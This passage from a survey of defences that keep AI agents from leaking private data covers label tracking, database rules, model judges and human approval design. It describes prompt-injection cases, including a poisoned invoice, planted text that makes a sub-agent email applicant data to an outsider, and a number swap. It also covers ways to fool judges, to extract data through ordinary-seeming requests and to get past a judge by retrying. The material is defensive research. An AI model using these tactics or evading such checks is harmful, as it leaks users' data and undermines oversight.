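Only 8 of the 19 test cases tried to send private data out, and the rest tried to overwrite protected files. All the attacks were prompt injections, so the results don't show how often Flowsh would stop an agent's own mistake. The approval counts assume a person who never makes a wrong decision. The delay is tolerable for most work. A shell call took 0.4 to 1 second, compared with less than 0.1 seconds in the lax sandbox, and completed tasks took 17% to 34% longer.

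### Remembering what the agent has already disclosed

A label stored on a laptop can't follow data to another company's server. If an agent gives an airline the user's passport number and fetches the booking confirmation a week later, the confirmation may contain that number without its label. *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (Stanley, Verma and colleagues, 2026) describes GAAP (Guaranteed Accounting for Agent Privacy), which keeps a log of such disclosures.

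In GAAP, as in CaMeL, the model writes a Python program instead of calling tools directly. GAAP analyses the program to find which private data could reach each tool call. But GAAP trusts much less than CaMeL does, assuming that an attacker may control the model and that even the user's prompt may contain an attack. It therefore keeps private values in its own database and gives the model only their names, such as "date of birth". GAAP treats showing the model a private file as a disclosure to the company that runs the model, and requires the user's permission for it.

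Before a tool call sends private data, GAAP checks for a saved decision on whether that recipient may receive that item. If there is none, it asks the user and normally saves the answer. It then logs the disclosure. When the same recipient later returns data, GAAP treats the data as possibly containing anything the recipient has already received, unless a description of the tool rules this out.

In one test, the user had let the agent copy `secret_info.txt` into a remote database. In a later task, the agent had to read that database and email the results. The new request didn't mention the file, but GAAP found it in the log and asked whether the email's recipient could have it.

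GAAP guarantees that outsiders learn only the private data the user has permitted them to have, even if an attacker controls everything the model writes. The guarantee doesn't cover private details that the user types into the prompt, or the timing and order of prompts. If the user uploaded a file without GAAP, the log has no record of it, and GAAP can only show the user a vaguer question about data from that service. GAAP protects only confidentiality, so a planted instruction could still make the agent delete something.

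The researchers tested GAAP against three planted instructions on 20 tasks with GPT-5, and it stopped every disclosure. One instruction told the agent to put the user's Social Security number wherever a phone number belonged. A second model acting as a judge missed every case of this swap, although the attack was possible in only two of the tasks. Without attacks, GAAP completed 76.0% of the tasks, compared with 81.0% for an unprotected agent. The gap was wider on AgentDojo, where GAAP completed 64.6% and the unprotected agent 80.1%.

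Over the 20 tasks, GAAP interrupted the user 39 times, or about twice per task, to ask for 55 permissions. With saved permissions erased after each task, it interrupted 58 times. Even two interruptions per task is a lot, though the number should fall as GAAP saves more of the user's answers.

Saving users' answers also carries a risk because GAAP identifies a file by its path. If Alex once allowed `sales.xlsx` to go to Marco, the permission would presumably still apply after someone saved the next quarter's unreleased figures in that file.

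### A private summary saved on Monday

Agents also keep data between requests. *SPA* gives the example of a user who asks an agent on Monday to fetch an invoice and save its details. An attacker has put their own account number in the invoice, so when the user asks the agent to pay it on Tuesday, the money goes to the attacker. Private data can leak after the same kind of delay. An agent might save a summary of a private configuration file on Monday and quote it in a public comment on Tuesday, when nothing in its context shows that the summary is private.

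SPA, developed at the University of South Florida, stores each result in three parts: the data, its label, and a description of what the data represents. On Tuesday, the planning model reads only the description. It writes a complete plan in a small language with six kinds of step, and it can use stored data only through a `retrieve` step, which also restores the label. Before any tool runs, a checker works through the plan:

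1. The plan retrieves Monday's summary, which has the label (trusted, private).
2. The plan passes the summary to the tool for public comments.
3. That tool may receive only public data, so the checker rejects the whole plan.

Because the checker has the whole plan, it can also cover implicit flows. Every step inside a branch gets the label of the branch's condition, and the checker examines both branches. Fenton's three-line program, which copied a secret into a variable labelled as public, wouldn't work in this language because a variable receives its value only once and a value set inside a branch isn't available outside it.

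If the checker rejects the planning model's plan, the request fails without a retry, because an attacker might otherwise use repeated attempts to find a plan that passes.

The researchers tested SPA with GPT-5.4 nano, a small model, on AgentDojo's 97 tasks. They also split each task into a conversation of two to five requests, so that later requests depended on stored results.

| | Single requests: tasks completed | Attacks succeeded | Conversations: tasks completed | Attacks succeeded |
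|---|---|---|---|---|
| SPA without label checks | 53.0% | 0.4% | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| SPA with label checks | 29.0% | 0.0% | 35.3% | 0.2% |

The checks nearly halved the number of completed tasks, and attacks rarely succeeded even without them. But most of the attacks planted instructions, which have little effect once the plan is fixed. The checks are meant for cases like the false account number, where the agent follows the right plan with the wrong data. *SPA* acknowledges that its attacks are a weak test of poisoned memory.

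Most of the rejected plans passed untrusted data to a tool that required trusted data. The drop in completed tasks therefore comes mainly from protecting integrity, and a policy that only kept private data from leaking might cause a much smaller drop.

### Rules for the rows behind a result

Labels on whole files or tool results are too coarse for databases. Suppose the maintainer asks an agent to publish the average timeout length in each region. The agent must read every customer's records to calculate the averages, so an ordinary label would mark even a harmless average as private. But in a region with only one customer, publishing the average would reveal that customer's own record.

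Summers (2026), in *Data Flow Control*, describes a system from Columbia University that applies rules to the rows behind each result. A rule for this case could require at least ten customers:

```
SOURCE Timeouts
CONSTRAINT COUNT(DISTINCT Timeouts.customer) >= 10
ON FAIL REMOVE
```

`SOURCE` names the table the rule protects, `CONSTRAINT` gives the condition, and `ON FAIL` determines whether to remove the offending result, change it or cancel the query. An optional `SINK` limits the rule to queries that write to a particular table.

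For each output row *o*, let *M*(*o*) be the list of combinations of input rows that produced it, and let *B* be the rule's condition. The row stays in the result if *B*(*M*(*o*)) is true. The rule uses this list because a database can calculate the same answer in different ways. It could record one derivation as *t*₁*s*₁ + *t*₁*s*₂ or as *t*₁(*s*₁ + *s*₂), and a rule that counted appearances of input rows would get four in the first case and three in the second.

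Recording every derivation can make a query up to 10,000 times slower. The Columbia system avoids this by adding the check to the query itself. If the agent asks for averages by region, the database in effect runs:

```
SELECT region, AVG(seconds) FROM Timeouts
GROUP BY region
HAVING COUNT(DISTINCT customer) >= 10
```

Regions with fewer than ten customers are left out of the result, regardless of what the agent intended. On a standard set of business queries run on five database systems, the checks added almost no time on average. One query slowed down noticeably because the system had to replace a quick test for matching rows with a full join.

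DAPLab, the Columbia group behind the project, also tested two frontier models as checkers. It gave them a tax rule and ten queries with their results, and asked whether each query broke the rule. Five did. Neither model was right more than 50% of the time, and GPT-5.5 reached 50% by rejecting every query. However, Summers reports that GPT-5.2 made no mistakes when judging whether the status changes in 1,000 updates were allowed, though it took about a hundred times as long as the database rule. Models may do well when the request contains the information they need, and badly when they have to match each result to the rows behind it.

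The database rules guarantee only that each query is acceptable on its own. An agent could use two permitted queries to get the total over eleven customers and then over ten of them, and subtract to find the eleventh customer's figure. *Please Don't Kill My Vibe* (2025), an earlier paper on the same approach, noted that a sequence of permitted queries could break a policy. A rule about data moving from `Receipts` to `Expenses` also doesn't apply if the agent copies the data through a third table. DAPLab is working on this problem and on tracking data between tool calls. For now, the rules can keep a customer's record out of a result, but they can't control where the agent sends a permitted result.

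The system also doesn't yet support some queries, including recursive ones. Rules can call a language model to judge, for example, whether a receipt is for a meal. *Agentic Data Environments* (2026) describes enforcement as deterministic even when they do, but such a rule is only as reliable as the model's answer.

### When one agent instructs another

Data can also lose its label when one agent passes work to another. In an experiment from *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, a user asked a main agent to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. One sub-agent read the applicants' details from a database, and another sent messages. Each agent ran its own copy of CaMeL, so text planted in the database couldn't change the plan of the agent that read it. But the main agent put the summary, including the planted text, into its instruction to the messaging agent, which trusted the whole instruction. The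 messaging agent followed the planted text and also emailed the applicants' details to an outsider.

Multi-CaMeL prevents this by separating the instruction from the data in each request between agents. The receiving agent's planning model never reads the data, which keeps its record of origin when it moves to the next agent. The software also blocks any instruction that depends on a tool's output.

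Across five models, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with separate copies, and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. On a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, separate copies reduced completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and multi-CaMeL reduced it by another 3.2. The additional loss from multi-CaMeL was under one point for the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5.

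These tests used no policies about private data. They show that planted instructions didn't cross between agents, but not that a customer's name would stay inside the company. Like CaMeL, Multi-CaMeL misses some implicit flows, and it covers only hierarchies in which each sub-agent has one parent.

*DelegateGuard* (2026) combines labels with permissions that the system can revoke, because even a correct label doesn't show whether a sub-agent should still be acting for the user. Each permission specifies its purpose, which agent holds it and which sinks that agent may use.

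### Who writes the labels and rules

All these systems depend on information that someone has to supply, and they respond differently when it is missing.

| System | Who supplies the labels and rules | What happens when one is missing |
|---|---|---|
| Flowsh | Whoever configures it sets the policy, the labels for sites and the defaults for files | The default applies. In the sample configuration, an unlabelled file is untrusted and only the user may read it |
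| GAAP | The user gives permissions, and an open-source community is meant to describe the tools | GAAP asks the user for a missing permission, and assumes the worst about a tool without a description |
| SPA | Whoever deploys the agent | The checker rejects a plan that retrieves a stored result without a label |
| Data Flow Control | Typically a database administrator | The query runs without restriction |
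| Multi-CaMeL | The software tracks origins, and the deployer writes any data policies | Instructions and data stay separate, but private data can go to any recipient |

Assuming the worst about a tool is safe only if users can handle the permission requests that result. Without descriptions of the file and email tools, GAAP would ask the user for permission to share everything in the file system with everyone the email server can reach, which no user could sensibly answer. With them, it can ask about sending one file to one address. Stanley and colleagues wrote descriptions for ten MCP servers, but somebody would have to write and check them for every other server a user connects.

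Data Flow Control's open default is easier to adopt because existing queries keep working. But if a company adds a table of customer records and forgets to write a rule, the agent can query it freely and nothing will warn anyone.

These defaults don't help when a label or rule exists but is wrong. If a tool's description wrongly says that a service never returns passwords, GAAP will label a returned password only as data from that service, so it may ask the user about sharing the data without mentioning a password. Labels can also become outdated. Zhou and Zhang point out that an agent may keep a cached result after it has lost access to the source. If Priya lets Marco read the sales figures and later changes her mind, a summary the agent saved in between may still list him as a permitted reader.

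## Deciding when private data may be released

People write release notes, customer replies and public bug fixes partly from private material. If software never let that material out, an agent couldn't write them either. It needs some way to declassify data, or deliberately release it despite its label. Suppose the maintainer's agent has read the company's private files and wants to publish one of these:

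- A release note says the library now waits 60 seconds before timing out, which anyone can check in the public code.
- A comment under a public issue says the bug appeared "while we were moving a large Ohio hospital group onto the paid service". A private file names the group, and the company hasn't announced the deal.
- A public pull request includes a screenshot of the internal billing console, to show that a fix works.

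The company would want to publish the first and withhold the other two. The permitted flow policy blocks all three, because everything the agent writes gets the private label of the agent's context. The company therefore needs another way to tell them apart. The table shows expected, not measured, results for three methods.

| Release | Scanner for known patterns | Model judge | Person who sees the exact content |
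|---|---|---|---|
| Release note | Allows it | Usually allows it | Usually allows it |
| Hospital comment | Allows it | Often blocks it, but may miss a paraphrase | Blocks it if they know about the deal and read carefully |
| Console screenshot | Allows it | Depends on whether it can read images or knows where the image is going | Blocks it if the request displays the image and they look at it |

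### What a scanner can recognise

Since August 2025, GitHub has scanned the inputs of all tool calls to public repositories through its hosted MCP server for secrets, which here means only passwords, keys and access tokens. By default, it blocks a call if it finds one. According to GitHub's current documentation, the protection also covers private repositories under its paid Advanced Security plan, though GitHub's *What is push protection?* still lists only public repositories.

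Scanning works well for credentials because they often have a distinctive format and almost never belong in a public comment. Each detector looks for a particular kind of credential. *GitHub adds 37 new secret detectors in March*, a 2026 news report, says the new detectors cover 22 providers and include six token types from the hosting company Vercel. Scanning also doesn't need labels, so it can catch a key that the agent found in an unlabelled file.

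The hospital comment contains nothing of this kind. The company could add the hospital group's name as a pattern, but the comment doesn't use the name. The screenshot gets through because the scanner reads only text. Software that extracts text from images could help catch a password displayed in the console, but not an ordinary billing record, which doesn't look like a credential. GitHub warned at launch that the feature wouldn't stop leaks of other data or leaks through channels it doesn't scan.

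A separate tool lets a developer ask the agent to scan its changes for secrets before committing them. GitHub (2026) made the tool generally available in May for repositories with GitHub Secret Protection. It can catch a key earlier, but only if someone asks for the scan.

### Model judges

A model judge can consider what a text means and who will receive it. OpenAI's coding agent Codex uses one, called Auto-review, to decide whether the agent may act outside its sandbox. OpenAI's *Auto-review* lists sending private data to untrusted destinations among the actions the judge should block. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026) report in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* that, in a sample of OpenAI's internal traffic, the judge approved 99.1% of requests to act outside the sandbox. It denied 90.3% of synthetic cases of overeager behaviour, which included unintended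 data transfers. The researchers also found ways to mislead the judge, and they don't expect such systems to provide firm guarantees.

A judge does better when ordinary software gives it the relevant facts. Anthropic hired Apollo Research, an AI safety company, to test the classifier in Claude Code's auto mode with synthetic attacks. Anthropic then gave the classifier more context, including whether a repository was public, and its miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. Before a push or pull request runs, the classifier now checks its destination, so it could flag the console screenshot without analyzing the image.

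A judge can block only the actions it checks. *Measuring the Permission Gate*, an independent test on deliberately ambiguous tasks, found that auto mode missed significantly more than Anthropic had reported, partly because it didn't monitor file edits.

### FlowSeal: tracking by rule, release by model

Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026), in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, combine conservative tracking with a model judge. Their system, FlowSeal, works as follows:

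1. Before the agent starts, someone registers each sensitive record with its owner, its text and the people who may receive it. Software can do part of this from existing access lists.
2. FlowSeal assumes from the start that any registered record may have influenced what the agent writes.
3. When the agent tries to write or share something, ordinary code looks up the recipient. It allows trusted recipients and blocks blacklisted ones.
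4. For anyone else, the code gives a separate model the exact text and every record that the recipient isn't authorised to see. The model answers SAFE or BLOCKED.
5. If the agent needs to share a record, it can ask the owner for consent.

The judge never reads the conversation, so a requester can't talk it into thinking that the disclosure is routine. (The requester may still influence the wording of the text it checks.)

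The researchers devised three attacks that used ordinary requests and no planted instructions. The attacks made disclosure look like normal shared work, or separated the request from the place where the data would appear. They extracted 43.8% to 75.6% of the sensitive items from an agent with strict consent rules in its prompt, and 0.5% to 2.3% with FlowSeal. With FlowSeal, the agent completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, close to the 75.9% it completed with the best of five other defences.

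The researchers also removed or changed parts of FlowSeal and repeated one of the attacks.

| Version | Sensitive items leaked | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Full FlowSeal | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| No guidance about FlowSeal for the agent | 8.8% | 74.4% |
| No check before writes | 28.4% | 81.2% |
| Judge always answers BLOCKED | 1.3% | 0.0% |
| Judge always answers SAFE | 24.9% | 79.4% |

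With a judge that always blocked, the agent completed nothing, because every recipient was unknown and the owners ignored requests for consent. The tracking rule alone was therefore useless for this work, and the model's judgement made release possible. Shim and colleagues describe the guidance as not critical to security, but the second row shows that without it the leak rate rose from 0.5% to 8.8%. The judge evidently misses some leaks, and an agent given the guidance probably attempts fewer.

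FlowSeal was much worse at releasing data when it should. In another test, where the requests were legitimate and the owners would consent if asked, the agent shared only 32.7% of the requested items under FlowSeal, compared with 61.0% to 85.6% under four other defences. Shim and colleagues attribute this to the agent asking for consent less often. But it still asked an average of 0.71 times per run, so less frequent asking probably explains only part of the gap.

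The FlowSeal paper proves that no text derived from a registered record can reach an unauthorised recipient unless the judge wrongly answers SAFE. The proof doesn't limit how often the judge makes this mistake, and the paper names paraphrase as the judge's main weakness. The hospital comment is a paraphrase of this kind. In one test, FlowSeal also released a health detail because nobody had registered it. The judge compares only text, so it would need a model that can read images to assess the screenshot.

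### Whether Fides relies on the model

Fides, the Microsoft system that hides restricted text in variables, enforces its policy with ordinary code. In the algorithm that Costa and colleagues give in the Fides paper, this code checks each tool call the model proposes against the policy and stops if the call fails the check. The model chooses which calls to propose, but it can't skip the check. Shim and colleagues say that the language model performs all policy enforcement in Fides and that their attacks would therefore work against it. They are wrong about the enforcement, and they didn't run Fides in their experiments.

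A confused agent could still leak data through Fides if the policy allowed the release. Under robust declassification, for instance, a misleading request from someone labelled as trusted might succeed. Permitted flow would block the same release if the labels were correct. FlowSeal depends more on a model than Fides with permitted flow does, because a model makes FlowSeal's final release decision.

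### Why people approve too much

A person may know things that no label or prompt contains, such as whether the company has announced the hospital deal. But people who see many requests stop reading them closely, which Anthropic calls *approval fatigue*. Claude Code users approve 97% of permission requests, but this alone doesn't show carelessness, because most requests are probably safe. Users also reject 39% of the plans Claude presents, so they don't approve everything they see.

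Anthropic also ran an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through a coding session, it replaced the text of one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of testers refused it, while auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers' refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests.

Anthropic published these results to explain why it was making auto mode the default. The testers weren't working on their own projects, and developers may be more careful when their own data is at stake. The commands also weren't limited to ones that would leak data. Even so, the drop during a session is what one would expect from fatigue.

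*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents mishandling files and found that flaws in user review contributed to 105. In 80 of these, the user had approved actions automatically. In 31, the approval request gave the user too little information, for example by naming a script without showing what it would do. Developers interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) said they clicked through familiar requests when they were short of time, so a long record of approvals doesn't necessarily show what users want.

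### A request that a person can judge

Microsoft suggests asking only when it matters, such as when an action would reveal information to someone who didn't already have access. The request can then show what data is involved and who would gain access to it. For the hospital comment, it might read:

> This comment may contain information from `customers.yaml` in the private repository. Anyone on the internet will be able to read it. The exact text is: "We found this while moving a large Ohio hospital group onto the paid service."

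For the screenshot, the request should display the image at a readable size. A file name such as `after-fix.png` wouldn't help.

*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) tests how much such details help. In one scenario, a user tells an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. The agent copies raw invoice rows into `report.csv` and asks to send that file. The auditor is an approved recipient and the file name looks normal, so a reviewer who sees only the last step has no reason to refuse.

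The study gave 80 volunteers one of four interfaces and 12 requests each, half of them unsafe.

| What the reviewer saw | Unsafe requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Exact details of the action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Those details, the user's original restriction and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
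| The same facts, with the relevant steps linked and their combined effect stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from showing more information, and it is uncertain whether organising it better helped. After adjustment, the last interface reduced unsafe approvals by 7.9 percentage points compared with the log, but the 95% interval runs from a reduction of 19.7 points to an increase of 3.8. It also didn't help with violations that depended on several linked steps, where reviewers approved 7 of 30 with either interface.

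Unsafe requests are probably much rarer in ordinary work. If 10 in 1,000 requests were unsafe and reviewers behaved as they did with the best interface, they would stop about 8 unsafe requests and refuse about 140 harmless ones, so about 95% of their refusals would be mistakes. Reviewers would probably respond by refusing less often, and would then miss more leaks.

Hossain and colleagues' design takes the facts in the request from recorded tool calls, because the agent's own description might be wrong. The software also checks again if the details change after approval. Otherwise the agent could post a different comment from the one a person approved.

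### Approvals given in advance

A standing exemption is an approval that someone gives before seeing the content. GitHub's `private-to-public-flows` setting is one example, and a policy that lets private data out of any trusted context has a similar effect. Exemptions save people from answering the same question repeatedly, but they often cover more than anyone intended.

In June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that let some shell commands run without approval. About 43% had allowed a general interpreter to run this way, such as Python, which can run almost any code. Trębacz and colleagues found the same kind of rule among a sizable minority of OpenAI's internal users. Auto mode now ignores these very broad rules because they would let commands bypass its classifier.

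People who don't write software may avoid deciding in advance what an agent can do. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people supervise a simulated assistant. Some approved each action individually, some had help from a model, and some first set rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of action. The rule-setters chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, leaving most decisions for later.

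People who set rules blocked about 20 percentage points less unrequested behaviour than people who reviewed each action. Their "allow" rules caused little of this, because 133 of the 148 unrequested actions that went ahead in the rules group were approved individually at the time. When the assistant asked to post publicly that the user was travelling, 15 of the 31 rule-setters who saw the request approved it, compared with 7 of the 34 people who reviewed every action. Setting rules may have made people feel they had already made the important decisions, but Yan's study doesn't establish why they blocked less. The groups also weren't fully random, because all later recruits joined the rules group.

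A safer exemption would name the source, the recipients, the type of content and an end date. For example, a maintainer could let text from `CHANGELOG.md` go to the public repository until Friday. The agent could then publish the release note, but not the hospital comment or the screenshot. This works only if the software can verify that the note came from the changelog alone. If the agent has also read `customers.yaml` in the same context, the note has that file's label too, and the exemption doesn't cover it.

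### Rules or judgement

Microsoft argues that security can't depend only on methods that sometimes fail. Labels and fixed policies give the same result every time, attackers can't change that result by persuasion, and people can audit them. Trębacz and colleagues make the opposite choice with Auto-review, which they write "sacrifices determinism for expressivity".

Arguments for judgement often start from *contextual integrity*, Helen Nissenbaum's theory that privacy depends on whether a flow of information suits its social context. Whether it does depends on who the information is about, who sends and receives it, what kind of information it is, and the terms on which it is shared. *Say Something Else* (2026) points out that a detail may be fine to tell a close friend but risky to tell a manager, and concludes that fixed filtering rules alone can't handle privacy.

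A scanner fails on that example because it looks only at the content, but a label that lists permitted readers can include the friend and leave out the manager. Labels have more trouble with purpose and detail. A hospital's technician may need to know which server is failing but not what the hospital pays for it, and one file may contain both facts. *Judging Before Propagation* (2026) instructs its model judge to read the actual text and permit only what suits the recipient's purpose, with no more detail than necessary.

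*Privacy Conductor* (2026) takes a middle position by writing contextual norms into document labels, which a predictable gate then applies. Its rules cover classes of people, so a rule can refer to doctors but not to one particular doctor. The gate enforces whatever policy it receives, good or bad. Some advocates of contextual integrity would object that determining whether a policy is good is the harder problem. *Privacy in Context Is Being Overlooked in the Age of General-Purpose LLMs* (2026) argues that reducing the theory to rule compliance loses what is distinctive about it, and that the theory needs more than algorithms.

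Much of this disagreement goes away if we split up the release decision.

| Part of the decision | What fixed rules can do | What needs judgement |
|---|---|---|
| Which private sources may have influenced the text? | Give a cautious answer from labels | Narrowing that answer |
| Who can read the destination? | Look it up | Usually nothing |
| May those people already read the sources? | Compare two lists | Usually nothing, if the lists are right |
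| Does the text reveal anything private? | Find known patterns | Recognising paraphrases and images |
| Is the disclosure appropriate? | Apply decisions that someone has already made | New cases, purpose and level of detail |
| Is this the text that the person approved? | Compare the two exactly | Nothing |

Rules can therefore settle many cases without anyone interpreting the text. If all the readers already have access to the sources, no further confidentiality check is needed. Cases like the release note and the hospital comment need judgement because their labels are identical and only their meaning differs.

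A judge model that can only block adds protection to a fixed rule, though its mistakes can block useful work. If it can override the rule and release data, protection depends on the model's error rate instead of the rule's guarantee. Retries make leaks more likely, because an agent may reword rejected text and try again, as agents did with FlowSeal. If a judge missed 10% of leaks and each attempt were independent, at least one of seven attempts would get through about half the time. OpenAI's Auto-review limits the number of attempts by stopping the run after repeated denials. The software could then pass the last version to a person, along with the earlier ones that the judge refused.
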